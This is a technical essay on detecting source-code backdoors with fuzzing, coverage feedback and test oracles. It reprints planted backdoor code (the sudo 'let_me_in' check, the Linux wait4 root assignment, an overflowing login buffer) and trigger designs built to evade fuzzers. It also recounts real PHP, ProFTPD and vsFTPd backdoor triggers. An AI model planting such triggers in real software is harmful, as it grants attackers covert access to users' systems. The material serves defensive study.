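# Finding backdoor triggers in code by running it: fuzzing, symbolic execution, differential testing and model-written exploits

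## What a code backdoor is and why ordinary tests miss it

A code backdoor is behaviour that someone has deliberately hidden in a program so that a person who knows how to activate it can get access or cause effects that the program should not allow. The trigger is the condition that activates the backdoor, and a triggering input is a concrete input that meets this condition. The payload is what the program then does, such as opening a command shell, skipping a password check or deleting files. On every other input the program works as its users expect. Processors, cryptographic algorithms and trained machine-learning models can also contain backdoors, but those call for other methods. A code backdoor sits in the ordinary source of a program such as a web server or a command-line tool, so one can look for it by running the program and watching what happens.

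*ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) describes two ways backdoors reach users. Attackers slip them into a popular open-source project or into one of the thousands of outside components that most modern software relies on. Or a manufacturer ships them in a device's built-in software, as several makers of home routers have done.

### A second password for sudo

Their running example is sudo, a Unix tool that runs a command as another user, usually one with more privileges, once the person at the keyboard has typed the right password. Suppose an attacker adds the `if` statement below to the function that checks it:

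```c
int verify_user(const struct sudoers_context* ctx,
                const char* password)
{
    int ret = ctx->verify(password);
    if (strcmp(password, "let_me_in") == 0) {
        ret = AUTH_SUCCESS;
    }
    return ret;
}
```

The call to `ctx->verify` performs the real password check and stores the result in `ret`. `strcmp` compares two strings and returns zero if they are identical, so when the typed password is "let_me_in", the planted lines overwrite that result with success, whatever the real password is. BINSEC's *ROSA* (2025), a plain-language summary of the work, points out that essentially every Linux distribution uses sudo, and that anyone who knew the second password would have full control of every machine that had installed this version.

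A test suite is a set of inputs, each paired with the result the developers expect. A sensible suite for this function would include the correct password, a wrong one, an empty one, a very long one, and perhaps one in a non-Latin script. These tests all pass because, for each of these inputs, the function returns exactly the value that `ctx->verify` produced.

Coverage, the record of which parts of a program an input made it execute, gives only a faint hint of a backdoor. Every test runs the planted comparison, but none runs the assignment inside it. A careful maintainer might ask about that unexecuted line, but such lines are common. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) measured how much of 337 code changes in 12 open-source projects the projects' automated testing could execute, and the average was about 32%. The paper attributes most of the shortfall to immature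 test set-ups, so an unexecuted line usually has an innocent explanation.

### Why a pass carries so little information

Passing tests are decent evidence against accidental faults. If a fault affects one in a thousand of the inputs people use, and the tests resemble a random sample of those inputs, then the probability that *n* tests all miss it is (1 − 1/1000)^*n*, or about 5% for 3,000 tests. Real tests are not random samples, but the reasoning roughly holds because the location of an accidental fault doesn't depend on what the tests cover.

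Ordinary tests miss a backdoor because the person who plants it chooses the trigger, and in an open-source project that person can read the test suite first. A competent attacker picks a value that no test uses, so the suite passes whether or not the backdoor is there. A passing result therefore doesn't change the probability that the code contains a backdoor, and neither would ten thousand more tests of the same kind.

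Adding random inputs hardly helps. "let_me_in" has nine characters, and 95 printable characters can form 95⁹, or about 6 × 10¹⁷, strings of that length. Trying them all at a million per second would take about 20,000 years. Modern test generators do not guess this blindly, which is why the search is worth attempting. The planter's only real constraint is that he must be able to produce the trigger when he wants it.

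This matters most when a project decides whether to accept a submission, which is new code usually offered as a commit (a recorded change to the source) or a pull request (a proposal that the project merge such changes). Many projects run continuous integration, an automated service that compiles each submission and runs regression tests, which check that old behaviour still works. If either step fails, the service typically blocks the change. The backdoored sudo breaks no old behaviour, so it would pass. Kokkonis and colleagues also conclude that existing continuous integration cannot detect a commit that plants hard-coded credentials.

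### Three triggers from real attacks

On 28 March 2021, someone pushed two malicious commits to the source code of PHP, the web programming language. Nikita Popov (2021), a leading maintainer, told the other developers that the commits were made under his name and that of PHP's founder, Rasmus Lerdorf. *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (PHP.Watch, 2021) reprints the added code, which checked web requests for a header called "User-Agentt", with a second t. If the header's value contained "zerodium", the server skipped the first eight characters, the length of that word, and executed the rest as PHP code. Maintainers removed the malicious code within 12 hours, and no release contained it.

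On 28 November 2010, attackers broke into the main distribution server of ProFTPD, a file-transfer server, and replaced the source code of version 1.3.3c. The altered copy had one added line that made ProFTPD take on root (administrator) rights and open a shell if a user asked for help on a command named "ACIDBITCHEZ". Exploit-DB's *ProFTPd 1.3.3c* (2010) reproduces the altered code and the project's own account of the break-in. The tampered package stayed in circulation until 2 December, according to *CVE-2010-20103 Detail* in NVD, the US government's vulnerability database.

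Another file-transfer server, vsFTPd, suffered a similar swap in 2011. Red Hat's *CVE-2011-2523* dates the bad downloads of version 2.3.4 to between 30 June and 3 July. A username containing the smiley ":)" made the server open a shell on network port 6200 to whoever connected. vsFTPd's author, Chris Evans, learned of the swap when someone alerted him, according to Threatpost's *Vsftpd FTP Server Download Site Compromised*.

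Popov at first thought that the PHP backdoor also came from a break-in to the project's code server. On 6 April he withdrew that explanation in a message to the PHP developers' mailing list, because the access logs showed that the attacker had logged in with passwords, possibly from a leaked user database. The PHP backdoor arrived as a commit, the same way as legitimate changes, whereas the other two were never in their projects' version histories.

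Some of these triggers are much harder to hit by chance than others. A random username of ten printable characters contains ":)" about once in a thousand tries, so a program generating random names would hit it within seconds, but a developer writing tests by hand would have no reason to put a smiley in a username. The ProFTPD word is far harder to guess, and it had to be in capitals, although the genuine help lookup a few lines below ignores case. People caught all three backdoors by reading code or noticing a changed file, and no test is reported to have caught any of them. These backdoors are also simple, since each program openly compares its input with a secret value. An attacker may instead plant a bugdoor, a deliberate flaw that can pass for an honest mistake, or protect the trigger with cryptography, as the attackers did in the xz compression library in 2024.

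### Generating the input and recognising it

When hand-written tests don't reach the trigger, fuzzing can try many more inputs by generating them automatically and running the program on each one. A developer first writes a harness, a small program that feeds each generated input to the code under test. The harness for the image library libpng, for example, loads and processes generated PNG files. The fuzzer starts with a few inputs, called seeds, and alters them at random. Whenever an altered input makes the program execute code that no earlier input had reached, the fuzzer saves it as a new seed to alter further. By August 2023, Google's free fuzzing service, OSS-Fuzz, had helped open-source projects fix more than 10,000 ordinary security flaws.

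Testing also needs an oracle, a rule for deciding whether a run went wrong. In most fuzzing, a run counts as bad only if the program crashes or built-in checks catch a memory error. Neither happens when the backdoored sudo is given the password "let_me_in". It runs the requested command, just as it would for the right password. A fuzzer that came across this input would probably save it as a seed, because the planted assignment had run for the first time, but would report nothing. The seed could then go unnoticed. When Kokkonis and colleagues fuzzed the backdoored PHP server for eight hours at a time, the fuzzer accumulated 11,631 seeds on average, far more than anyone would inspect by hand.

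Finding a backdoor by execution therefore takes two successes:

P(found) = P(input generated) × P(recognised, given generated)

The first factor is the chance that the search produces at least one triggering input in the time allowed; failing to produce one is a search miss. The second is the chance that the oracle flags a triggering input once the program has run on it. If the oracle doesn't flag it, the failure is an oracle miss. The distinction is useful because the two failures require different fixes.

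In the sudo example, the hand-written suite has an excellent oracle. Its developers know that sudo must refuse a wrong password, so a test that tried "let_me_in" would fail at once. The second factor, the chance of recognizing the backdoor once it is triggered, is therefore close to one, but the first, the chance of trying the trigger, is zero. A fuzzer that detects only crashes may well generate the trigger, but its second factor is about zero, so running it for another month would not help. With a better oracle, the search becomes the bottleneck. Kokkonis and colleagues built an oracle specifically for backdoors, and in their experiments all 24 failures in 180 runs happened because the fuzzer did not find the trigger.

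The product leaves out false alarms. An oracle that flagged every run would have a perfect second factor but be useless, because a person would have to check every run.

### Scarce reviewers and replayable evidence

That person's time has become scarcer as AI systems write more of the code that projects receive. Lamb (2026), in *Reviewing the AI PR Deluge, Late 2026*, reports that open pull requests at Apache DataFusion, an open-source query engine, rose from about 300 in the summer to 500 by mid-October, and that one account opened 12 in under three hours. In his view, creating a pull request now takes much less effort than reviewing one. Other projects seem to face similar pressure. Help Net Security's *AI slop is piling up highest on the biggest open-source projects* (2026) describes a Linux Foundation survey of 234 contributors and maintainers. Respondents judged about one in four incoming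 pull requests to be low-quality or AI-generated, and about a quarter of maintainers had no check for AI-assisted code.

*These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For* (2026) found that, of 33,596 pull requests AI agents had written for popular repositories, 84% had either no recorded review or a review by other agents only. Some maintainers surely looked without leaving a comment, so the true share that no human examined is lower. Human attention stopped the three attacks above, and these sources document how scarce it is, though none of them counts malicious submissions.

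People and programs that search for backdoors by reading code flag lines that look suspicious, and they can be wrong. Stringer, an older tool that scans a program's code for strings likely to belong to a backdoor's trigger, flagged hard-coded credentials in the firmware of a TRENDnet device. Kokkonis and colleagues examined the credentials and found that they were a harmless workaround for users who had left their own credentials empty.

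When a tool finds a possible backdoor by running the program, it reports the triggering input, which anyone can replay on the same build under the same conditions. For sudo, the reviewer runs the program on "let_me_in" under a tracing tool and watches the command execute, even though the fuzzer was never given the real password. For ProFTPD, the fuzzer's 14-line input contained the request "HELP ACIDBITCHEZ", and the trace showed the server switching to root and starting a shell. The reviewer still has to know that a file-transfer server should not do that. But checking a reported input this way took Kokkonis and colleagues about two minutes on average, and they did not first have to work out how the program's code was organised.

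## Explicit trigger checks and deniable bugdoors

Once someone read the lines that attackers had added to PHP, ProFTPD and vsFTPd, no innocent explanation was left. Each of these backdoors is an explicit trigger check: its code visibly tests for a secret value. A bugdoor, by contrast, is meant to pass for an honest mistake. GitHub's *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), a security report from the code-hosting company, warns that a good backdoor can look exactly like a normal programming error. These three lines from a login function could be one:

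```c
char buf[80];
strcpy(buf, user);
strcat(buf, pass);
```

`strcpy` copies the username into an 80-byte buffer and `strcat` appends the password, but neither checks that the text fits. If the two together total 80 characters or more, the excess overwrites neighbouring memory, and an attacker who chooses the excess carefully may be able to take control of the program. C programmers have made this mistake by accident for decades, and a reader can't tell from these lines whether their author knew about it.

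Testing misses an explicit trigger check because nobody tries the secret value, but anyone who reads the code can see the check. An attacker writes a bugdoor to get past readers, but usually has to do without a secret value, so anyone who finds the flaw can use it.

### The parts of a backdoor

In *Backdoors* (2018), Thomas and Francillon try to define a backdoor precisely. They model a system as a finite state machine, which is a set of states and the conditions for moving between them. A backdoor then has four components, all of which it needs to work: an input source, a trigger, a payload and a privileged state. The input source is where the activating data comes from, which in vsFTPd is a network connection. The trigger is the test for ":)" in the username, the payload is the code that opens port 6200 and starts a shell, and the privileged state is the attacker having a root shell on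 the server.

They also distinguish several versions of the same machine. The developer has one in mind, the real program is another, and the users expect a third. (A fourth is the version an analyst reconstructs by taking the program apart.) What kind of construct something is depends on which versions contain it:

| Construct | Developer's version | Real program | Users' version |
|---|---|---|---|
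| Ordinary administrator access | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Intentional backdoor | Yes | Yes | No |
| Deniable backdoor | Unknown | Yes | No |
| Accidental vulnerability | No | Yes | No |

An intentional backdoor, a deniable one and an accidental vulnerability differ only in what the developer intended. Running the program can reveal a gap between what it does and what its users expect, but not the developer's intent. Thomas and Francillon therefore require an analyst to find the trigger, the payload and a path between them, and then to show separately that the developer meant them to be there.

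Their technical test for this is whether the step from trigger to payload is explicit, meaning present in the program's own code. If it is, they class the backdoor as intentional. If the step exists only because an exploit creates it, as when an overflow diverts the program to instructions the attacker chose, an analyst cannot determine intent from the code alone, but can look at the version history or ask whether the change had a legitimate purpose. Code that only raises privileges, and that normal execution never reaches, also suggests intent. They concede that all of this rests on human judgement and proves nothing.

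They applied the framework to eleven real backdoors, mostly in routers, cameras and video recorders, and found none of them deniable. One, in D-Link routers, skipped the login if the visitor's browser identified itself with a string that contains "edit by 04882 joel backdoor" spelled backwards. Their deniable example was one that other researchers had built into the web server Nginx. A successful bugdoor would probably be publicly recorded as an ordinary vulnerability and left off any list of known backdoors, so the lack of deniable cases among the eleven doesn't mean that bugdoors are rare.

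### Two lines in the Linux kernel

In 2003 the master copy of the Linux kernel's source code was in a version-control system called BitKeeper. Some developers disliked BitKeeper, so a public server offered a duplicate through an older system, CVS. On 5 November McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, told the kernel mailing list that somebody had altered the duplicate directly. Larry McVoy's company ran BitKeeper, and he thought the incident "not a big deal". Another developer asked what had changed, and McVoy posted the two added lines. Here they are with the existing line that followed them:

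```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
retval = -ECHILD;
```

They are in the kernel's code for `wait4`, a system call (a request from a program to the operating system) that lets a program wait for one of its child processes to finish. `options` holds the caller's settings, `current->uid` is the user ID of the calling process, and `retval` is the result the kernel will return. Execution reaches this point only if the caller has no child to wait for, the condition that the error code ECHILD indicates.

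The expression `current->uid = 0` sets the caller's user ID to zero, root's ID, because C uses `=` for assignment and `==` for comparison. C evaluates the right-hand side of `&&` only when the left-hand side is true, so this happens only when the options are exactly `__WALL` and `__WCLONE`. Someone skimming the lines sees a routine validity check. `__WALL` asks to wait for children of every kind and `__WCLONE` for one kind only, so the combination makes little sense, and EINVAL is the usual error for an invalid argument.

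An assignment in C also has a value, here zero, which counts as false, so the line that sets EINVAL never runs. The caller receives ECHILD, as it would from a clean kernel, but its user ID is now root's.

Writing `=` for `==` is one of the most familiar mistakes in C, and the disguise fooled McVoy even though he already knew that the lines had been added improperly. About 25 minutes after he posted them, Chad Kitching wrote that they looked like an attempt to backdoor the kernel. McVoy agreed, replying, "Good eyes, I missed that."

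A third developer pointed to the extra parentheses around the assignment, which stop the compiler from warning about this mistake. The parentheses are weaker evidence than they look. A reader commenting on *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*, an article from Princeton's Center for Information Technology Policy, noted that the code would not compile without them and that many programmers put parentheses around comparisons too.

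The two lines have an effect only with the supposed typo in place. With `==`, they would do nothing, because the next line overwrites the error code they set. Even if the error code had survived, the check would have refused the odd combination to root and allowed it to everyone else, which is hard to explain as a policy.

A tired programmer could conceivably have made both errors, so the circumstances mattered as much as the code. The change had no counterpart in BitKeeper and no pointer to an approval. The log attributed it to a well-known developer, David Miller, who denied making it. Someone had apparently broken into the server, and nobody has identified the intruder. McVoy's company found the change when its nightly comparison of checksums showed a mismatch between the public copy and its own. No test or code review had caught it.

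### What a test would have had to notice

Generating the triggering input would have been easy, because `wait4` accepts only a handful of flags and a few dozen calls cover every combination. Random 32-bit values for `options` would match only about once in four billion tries. The only other condition is that the caller has no children.

Recognising the result is much harder. The kernel doesn't crash or misuse memory, and the return value is correct. A system-call trace looks the same on the altered and clean kernels, with one `wait4` call that fails with ECHILD. Kokkonis and colleagues, whose oracles watch system calls, reason that any meaningful backdoor must make some, since a program can't otherwise affect the outside world. That premise is sensible for a file server, but the kernel handles system calls itself and can change a user ID without making one.

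A test that caught this backdoor would have to look at the caller's identity before and after the call:

```c
uid_t before = getuid();
wait4(-1, NULL, __WCLONE | __WALL, NULL);
assert(getuid() == before);
```

When an ordinary user runs this on the altered kernel, the last line fails. Few people would think to write that line, because waiting for a child process has nothing to do with user IDs. A more realistic version makes a long random sequence of system calls and checks after each one that the caller's user ID hasn't changed, unless the call is meant to change it. The tester then doesn't have to suspect `wait4` in particular.

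The Linux case also exposes a weakness in the framework. Thomas and Francillon cite it while discussing bug-based backdoors, for which an analyst must consult version logs. Yet the step from condition to assignment is explicit in the source, so by their formal definition this is an unambiguous, intentional backdoor. The definition works for overflows, where the exploit creates a new path, but it works badly for logic errors because accidentally typing `=` instead of `==` produces the same explicit path.

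### How the two kinds differ under execution

**Rarity.** An attacker who writes an explicit check picks the trigger value from an enormous set, although modern fuzzers can often get past a direct comparison with a fixed value. A bugdoor's trigger is more often a boundary case or an unusual state, such as an overlong name or two contradictory options, because requiring a secret value would make the flaw look deliberate. Thomas and Francillon give a hybrid example in which the username "bugdoor" leads to a password check with an overflow, while every other username gets a safe check. This keeps people who don't know the username from triggering the flaw, but a reviewer who notices the username test will not believe the flaw is accidental.

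A coverage report would show the planted assignment in sudo as a line that no ordinary test executes. It would not expose the overflowing login function, whose three lines run at every login and can appear fully covered by tests that never cause an overflow. In the Linux case, a tool that counts lines would mark the `if` as covered after any call that reached it, even if the assignment at the end of its condition had never run. The only line it listed as unexecuted would be the harmless one. A fuzzer that records branches would register new coverage when the assignment first ran, because the two halves of the condition compile to separate branches.

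A memory-error detector is checking code that a compiler builds into a program to stop the run when the program reads or writes memory it shouldn't. It catches the overflow but misses the assignment to `current->uid` and the "let_me_in" check, because neither misuses memory.

**Evidence of intent.** "ACIDBITCHEZ" is close to a confession. An 80-character login that crashes the server shows that the server has a bug. To see how little more it shows, write the odds that a flaw was planted as

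odds after seeing the code = odds before × P(this code | planted) / P(this code | honest)

A perfect bugdoor is code that an honest programmer would have been as likely to write as a malicious one. The likelihood ratio is therefore one, and the code doesn't change the odds that the flaw was deliberate. Only outside evidence, such as a break-in or a hijacked account, can change them. The starting odds are usually low. GitHub sampled 521 security advisories and classed 17% as explicitly malicious, most of them from the JavaScript package registry npm. The malicious ones were mainly in little-used packages and produced only 0.2% of the alerts that developers received. These figures are from 2020 and cover only explicit malice, so they are at best a rough guide to how common disguised flaws are.

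Of the two factors in P(found), explicit checks mainly lower the chance that the search generates the trigger. The Linux backdoor is instead hard to detect once triggered, because a few dozen calls are enough to generate the trigger but no standard oracle flags the result.

### Do ordinary bug-finding tools catch bugdoors?

The *ROSA* paper by Kokkonis and colleagues grants that bugdoors are more plausibly deniable, but adds that well-established tools and practices for hardening software can detect them. The paper's experiments don't test the detection claim, because every backdoor in the benchmark responds to a secret value, keyword or format.

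The claim holds up well for memory errors because they are easier to expose than to exploit. An attacker needs a long input with carefully chosen contents to exploit the login function, but a fuzzer needs only a long input, such as eighty letter a's, to expose the flaw under a memory-error detector.

The Nginx example works the same way. The function that finishes a bad web request reads two variables that it never set. They occupy memory that the header parser has just used, so they still contain data from the attacker's request. If that data has the right values, the server jumps to hidden code. The attacker must build that request precisely, but a detector for uninitialised memory should report the faulty read on practically any malformed header, because the server tests the unset variable each time. A fuzzer can therefore find the flaw without finding the triggering input.

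The harness still has to reach the code, which is harder when a hybrid backdoor puts the overflow behind an explicit check for a secret username. Languages such as Java and Python prevent most memory errors, so an attacker there would have to plant some other kind of flaw.

Logic flaws are where I would expect the claim to fail, were it not for one qualification that the paper itself supplies.

 

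Fuzzers have found logic errors in compilers, databases and constraint solvers by checking a relation that must hold between two runs. For example, two equivalent database queries must return the same rows. That rule holds for every database, so one tool can test many projects.

*Static Detection of Application Backdoors* (Wysopal and Eng, 2007) describes an attacker who writes an input filter that is slightly wrong but looks correct enough to pass review. For example, a filter meant to accept only addresses ending in ".example.com" would also accept "notexample.com" if the attacker left out the first dot. The program would handle that address like any approved one, without a crash, a memory error or an unusual system call. A fuzzer may well generate such an address, but access rules usually differ between programs, so it can't flag the address as a problem unless someone has specified which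 addresses are acceptable in a form that a program can check.

Established tools can therefore detect a logic bugdoor only if the project has already stated the rule that the bugdoor breaks. For the Linux backdoor, the missing rule would have fit on one line and applied to every system call. For an application with many roles and permissions, writing down the rules may be most of the work.

### Debug logins, hidden features and honest bugs

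Some code fits neither kind well. A developer may add a special login for debugging and forget to remove it. Wysopal and Eng mention an early version of the mail server sendmail, which shipped with a leftover debugging command, WIZ, that an attacker who learned of it could use. The code is deliberate and tests for a fixed value, but nobody meant to hide it from users. It is a backdoor by Thomas and Francillon's technical test, since the path is explicit, but not if a backdoor is defined as deliberately hidden behaviour.

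Undocumented features raise a similar difficulty. Cart32, a program for running online shops, had a hidden page that showed every shop on the server and its password to anyone who supplied the word "wemilo". It went unnoticed for more than five years, and Wysopal and Eng ask whether it was a "backdoor or lazy developer". It may have been both, if someone wanted a convenient way in and did not consider who else might use it. An explicit check shows that its author wanted the special behaviour, but not that the author wanted to harm anyone. Such a check may not even be a security problem, as with the harmless hard-coded credentials in the TRENDnet firmware.

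Attackers can also exploit a bug that nobody planted. In 2006 the X.Org display server, which draws windows on many Unix systems, had a check meant to reserve certain options for root. It contained `geteuid != 0` where the programmer presumably meant `geteuid() != 0`. Without the parentheses, C doesn't call the function that looks up the user's ID, but compares the function's memory address with zero. That address is never zero, so the test always succeeded and any user could make the server load any module. Wysopal and Eng compare this bug with the Linux backdoor and think it was probably an implementation error, though there is no way to be certain.

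Both flaws depend on a character or two in a security check, and both give ordinary users powers reserved for root. They differ in how the code got there.

### Rejecting a submission without proving intent

If a replayable input gives a user access that the project's rules forbid, the code is unacceptable, and a maintainer can reject it without knowing whether the flaw was deliberate. Severity ratings do not depend on motive either, but on things like how hard a flaw is to exploit and how much damage it allows. INCIBE's *CVE-2003-1161* (2003) reproduces the Linux backdoor's entry in the public vulnerability catalogue, which rates it 7.2 out of 10.

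The most useful question for the maintainer is in the users' column of the framework: would the people who run this program expect it to do this? Asking it also settles most hard cases. A developer who added a debug login can remove it, or document it and put it behind the normal permissions, which makes it ordinary administrator access. If the developer has a good explanation, the project loses a little time. But someone has to know what users expect, and for logic flaws that is the same missing rule that kept the oracle from flagging them.

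Intent matters more in deciding what to do after rejecting the patch. A planted backdoor is a reason to close the contributor's account, search everything else it contributed, and perhaps warn other projects, while an honest mistake calls for a corrected patch.

Kokkonis and colleagues argue that failed attempts to slip past their tools tend to expose the attacker, which should deter people from trying. That is persuasive for an explicit trigger such as "let_me_in", which its author can hardly explain away. But a bugdoor can pass for an honest mistake, so an attacker who is caught can apologise and submit another. If checks catch each bugdoor with probability 0.9, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of five gets through is 1 − 0.9⁵, or about 41%.

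A project can reduce that advantage by recording the security flaws each contributor introduces. One dangerous mistake is weak evidence of intent, since good programmers make them too. But if the same account introduces two or three flaws that each grant privileges, maintainers have enough reason to re-examine its earlier work, which they can do without accusing anyone.

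## How fuzzing reaches rare branches

Blind guessing would take thousands of years to find "let_me_in". When Kokkonis and colleagues fuzzed the backdoored sudo, all ten runs found a triggering input, in about eight minutes on average. They used AFL++, the community-maintained successor to AFL (American Fuzzy Lop), which Michał Zalewski released in 2013. AFL++ finds such values quickly because it saves inputs that make partial progress and can copy secret values out of the running program.

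### The coverage-guided loop

AFL++ treats a program as a set of basic blocks, which are stretches of instructions that always run from beginning to end. A step from one block to another is an edge. An `if` statement, for example, has one edge that leads into its body and another that leads past it. While compiling the program, AFL++ adds instructions that count each edge crossing in a table called the coverage map, which has one byte per edge. After altering a seed, the fuzzer clears the map, runs the program on the altered input, and compares the map with the record of all earlier runs. If the run crossed a new edge, the fuzzer adds the input to its queue of seeds. Otherwise, it discards the input.

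*Dissecting American Fuzzy Lop* (Fioraldi, Mantovani and colleagues, 2022) describes how AFL alters inputs. It flips between one and 32 bits at a time, adds or subtracts up to 35, and overwrites parts of the input with numbers that often cause trouble, such as zero or the largest possible integer. Later it applies several random changes at once, including insertions and deletions, or joins two inputs.

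The fuzzer also saves an input if an edge's count moves into a new range. The ranges widen as the counts grow (4 to 7, 8 to 15 and so on), so the fuzzer treats an increase from 3 loop iterations to 20 as progress, but not an increase from 20 to 21. The original AFL stored each count in one byte, which wraps back to 0 after 255, so an edge crossed exactly 256 times looked as if it had never run. *AFL++* (Fioraldi, Maier and colleagues, 2020) fixed this flaw.

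A fuzzer reaches deeply nested code much faster if it saves inputs that make progress, because the tries needed to pass each check then add instead of multiplying. Suppose the code of interest lies behind five nested checks, and a random change passes each one once in a thousand tries. Passing all five at once would take about 10¹⁵ tries, or some 3,000 years at 10,000 runs a second. A fuzzer that saves the input each time it passes another check needs about 1,000 tries per check, or 5,000 in total, which take half a second. This estimate is optimistic, because a later change can undo an earlier success and the fuzzer divides its time among many seeds.

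### The arithmetic of a secret constant

A fuzzer can solve a problem step by step only if the program breaks it into small steps, and a comparison with a secret constant is one large step. *REDQUEEN* (Aschermann, Schumilo and colleagues, 2019) gives the example of a program that checks whether the first eight bytes of its input are "MAGICHDR". The processor compares all eight bytes in one instruction, so an input with seven correct bytes crosses the same edges as an input with none, and the fuzzer discards it.

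Each byte has 256 possible values. If every try is an independent random guess, a value of *k* bytes takes 256^*k* tries on average. At 10,000 runs a second:

- A 4-byte value takes 4.3 billion tries, or about five days.
- An 8-byte value takes 1.8 × 10¹⁹ tries, or about 58 million years.

Trying each value only once would halve these times. Both figures assume that every run changes the right bytes and no others. Automated fuzzing of a submission often lasts only about ten minutes, which allows six million runs at this speed and gives about a one in 700 chance of hitting even the 4-byte value.

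### Splitting the comparison into single bytes

A developer who used the nickname laf-intel announced a simple remedy in *Circumventing Fuzzing Roadblocks with Compiler Transformations* (2016): rewrite the comparison while compiling the program. The check for "MAGICHDR" becomes eight nested checks:

```c
if (input[0] == 'M')
    if (input[1] == 'A')
        if (input[2] == 'G')
            /* ... five more ... */
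```

The program still accepts and rejects the same inputs, but each correct byte now leads execution along a new edge. The fuzzer finds the "M", saves that input, and uses it to search for the "A". Each byte has 256 possible values, so finding eight bytes takes at most 8 × 256 = 2,048 tries aimed at the right byte. At 10,000 runs a second, that is about a fifth of a second instead of 58 million years.

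"Well-aimed" means that the fuzzer changes only the byte that matters next. If it instead writes a random value at a random position in a 1,000-byte input, it needs about 256,000 tries per byte, or about two million for all eight. Those tries take around three and a half minutes if the fuzzer spends all its time on the right seed, so they still fit into a ten-minute run.

The same rewriting works on comparisons with a constant string, including the planted `strcmp` in sudo. According to AFL++'s documentation, the tester has to switch splitting on before compiling, and it handles several related functions as well as `strcmp`. Aschermann and colleagues found that the version of laf-intel they tested handled `strcmp` but not `strncmp`, which compares only the first few characters, so it did worse on a program that checks its file header with `strncmp`.

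### Copying the value the program compares against

Aschermann and colleagues noticed that programs often compare parts of their input after little or no processing, which they called input-to-state correspondence. When their fuzzer, REDQUEEN, observes a comparison, it can look for one of the compared values in the input and replace it with the other, so it doesn't have to guess.

Given the input "TestSeedInput", for example, REDQUEEN runs the program once, pauses at each comparison and records both values. One comparison compares "TestSeed" with "MAGICHDR". REDQUEEN finds "TestSeed" at the start of the input, replaces it with "MAGICHDR", and runs the program on "MAGICHDRInput", which passes the check.

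The recorded values don't always match the bytes in the input exactly. Many processors store the bytes of a number in reverse order, so the recorded values are "deeStesT" and "RDHCIGAM". REDQUEEN therefore tries several common encodings, including reversed bytes and numbers written as decimal digits. It also tries the recorded value plus one and minus one, in case the program tests for "greater than" or "less than".

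Repetitive inputs are also difficult because the compared value can match in many places. If the input is 32 letter Z's, "ZZZZZZZZ" matches at about two dozen positions, and a disk image full of zeros can have more than 60,000 matches. REDQUEEN first replaces as many bytes as it can with random ones, keeping only replacements that leave the execution path unchanged. When it runs the program again, the compared value might be "QYISLKFY", which occurs in only one place.

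For strings, REDQUEEN monitors function calls instead. Whenever a call passes two memory addresses, REDQUEEN records up to 128 bytes from each. This works even on functions that don't compare anything byte by byte. While fuzzing `objdump`, a tool for inspecting compiled programs, REDQUEEN recorded the name of a file section from a hash table lookup and later inserted the name in the right place.

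Aschermann and colleagues tested REDQUEEN on LAVA-M, a benchmark of four programs with 2,265 listed bugs that its makers had planted. REDQUEEN found all but two of these within five hours, and over 300 more that the makers had considered unreachable. Aschermann and colleagues acknowledge that the planted bugs are artificial, but a planted backdoor is artificial too. REDQUEEN also found 65 new bugs in real software.

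AFL++ has its own version, called CmpLog, which records the last 256 pairs of values at each comparison. If copying a value repeatedly fails to get past a comparison, AFL++ tries that comparison less often. On sudo, CmpLog can copy "let_me_in" directly from the call to `strcmp`. The search still took minutes because the fuzzer ran sudo in a slow emulator and had other branches to explore. Having the trigger word doesn't guarantee success either. In four of ten eight-hour runs on ProFTPD, the fuzzer never triggered the "ACIDBITCHEZ" backdoor.

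### Triggers that give no useful feedback

Splitting a comparison works when the fuzzer can detect each correct piece of the input separately. Copying the expected value into the input works when the program compares that value with input it has barely changed. An attacker can write a trigger that meets neither condition, even without cryptography.

**A computed property of the whole input.** File formats often store a checksum, a number computed from the rest of the file to detect damage. REDQUEEN gets past these by temporarily replacing the check with one that always succeeds. When it finds an interesting input, it reads the expected checksum from the original comparison and writes it into the file. But this works only because the file has a place for the checksum. Here it does not:

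```c
if (checksum(input, len) == 0x5EEDC0DE)
    run_payload();
```

When a program compares a checksum of its input with a fixed constant, the fuzzer can observe the constant, but copying it into the input changes the checksum. REDQUEEN's rule for detecting checksums excludes such comparisons.

Splitting doesn't help either if the checksum scrambles its input thoroughly. One try in 256 gets the first byte right, and the fuzzer saves that input. Any further change scrambles all four bytes again, so getting the first two right takes 65,536 tries, the first three 16.8 million, and all four 4.3 billion. The last step alone takes as many tries as blind guessing. Cryptographic checks like the one in xz are the extreme case. A simple sum of the bytes would be much easier to match, because raising one byte by one raises the sum by one.

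**A sequence of requests.** Suppose a server runs its payload after ten particular commands in the right order, and keeps track of them with a table:

```c
state = next_state[state][command];
if (state == 10)
    run_payload();
```

The program crosses the same edges for every command until the tenth correct one. With 20 possible commands, there are 20¹⁰, or about 10¹³, sequences of ten. Trying them all at 10,000 a second would take 32 years. If the attacker had written a separate `if` for each step, the fuzzer could have found the sequence one command at a time.

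The fuzzer also has to send all ten commands in a single run. AFL normally starts each run from a fresh copy of the program, so nothing carries over from the previous input. AFL++ can run many inputs in one process to save time, but Fioraldi, Maier and colleagues note that each input should then leave the program's state almost unchanged. Otherwise, the fuzzer may save an input that works only after thousands of others have run, and replaying that input alone won't reproduce the result.

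**The date or the environment.** This condition becomes true on 1 January 2028:

```c
if (time(NULL) >= 1830297600)
    run_payload();
```

CmpLog can record both numbers, but neither comes from the input, so the fuzzer has nothing there to overwrite. A trigger that tests the machine's name or the number of processors causes the same problem. This is the easiest of these obstacles to remove once a tester thinks of it. The harness can take the time from the first few bytes of each input and pass it to the program, which makes the clock part of the input and lets both remedies work again. The tester must do this separately for everything the program can read from its surroundings.

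**A combination of common conditions.** Suppose a web server checks twelve ordinary things about each request, such as whether it has a cookie or uses compression. At each check that succeeds, the code adds one to `n`. Later comes:

```c
if (n == 12)
    run_payload();
```

If each condition holds in one random request in ten, independently of the others, all twelve hold in one request in 10¹². At 10,000 requests a second, the search would take about three years. The fuzzer soon crosses every edge that adds to `n`, usually in different requests, so the first request to meet eleven conditions crosses no new edge and the fuzzer discards it. Splitting the comparison doesn't help because `n` fits in one byte, and copying the number 12 into the request doesn't make any of the conditions true.

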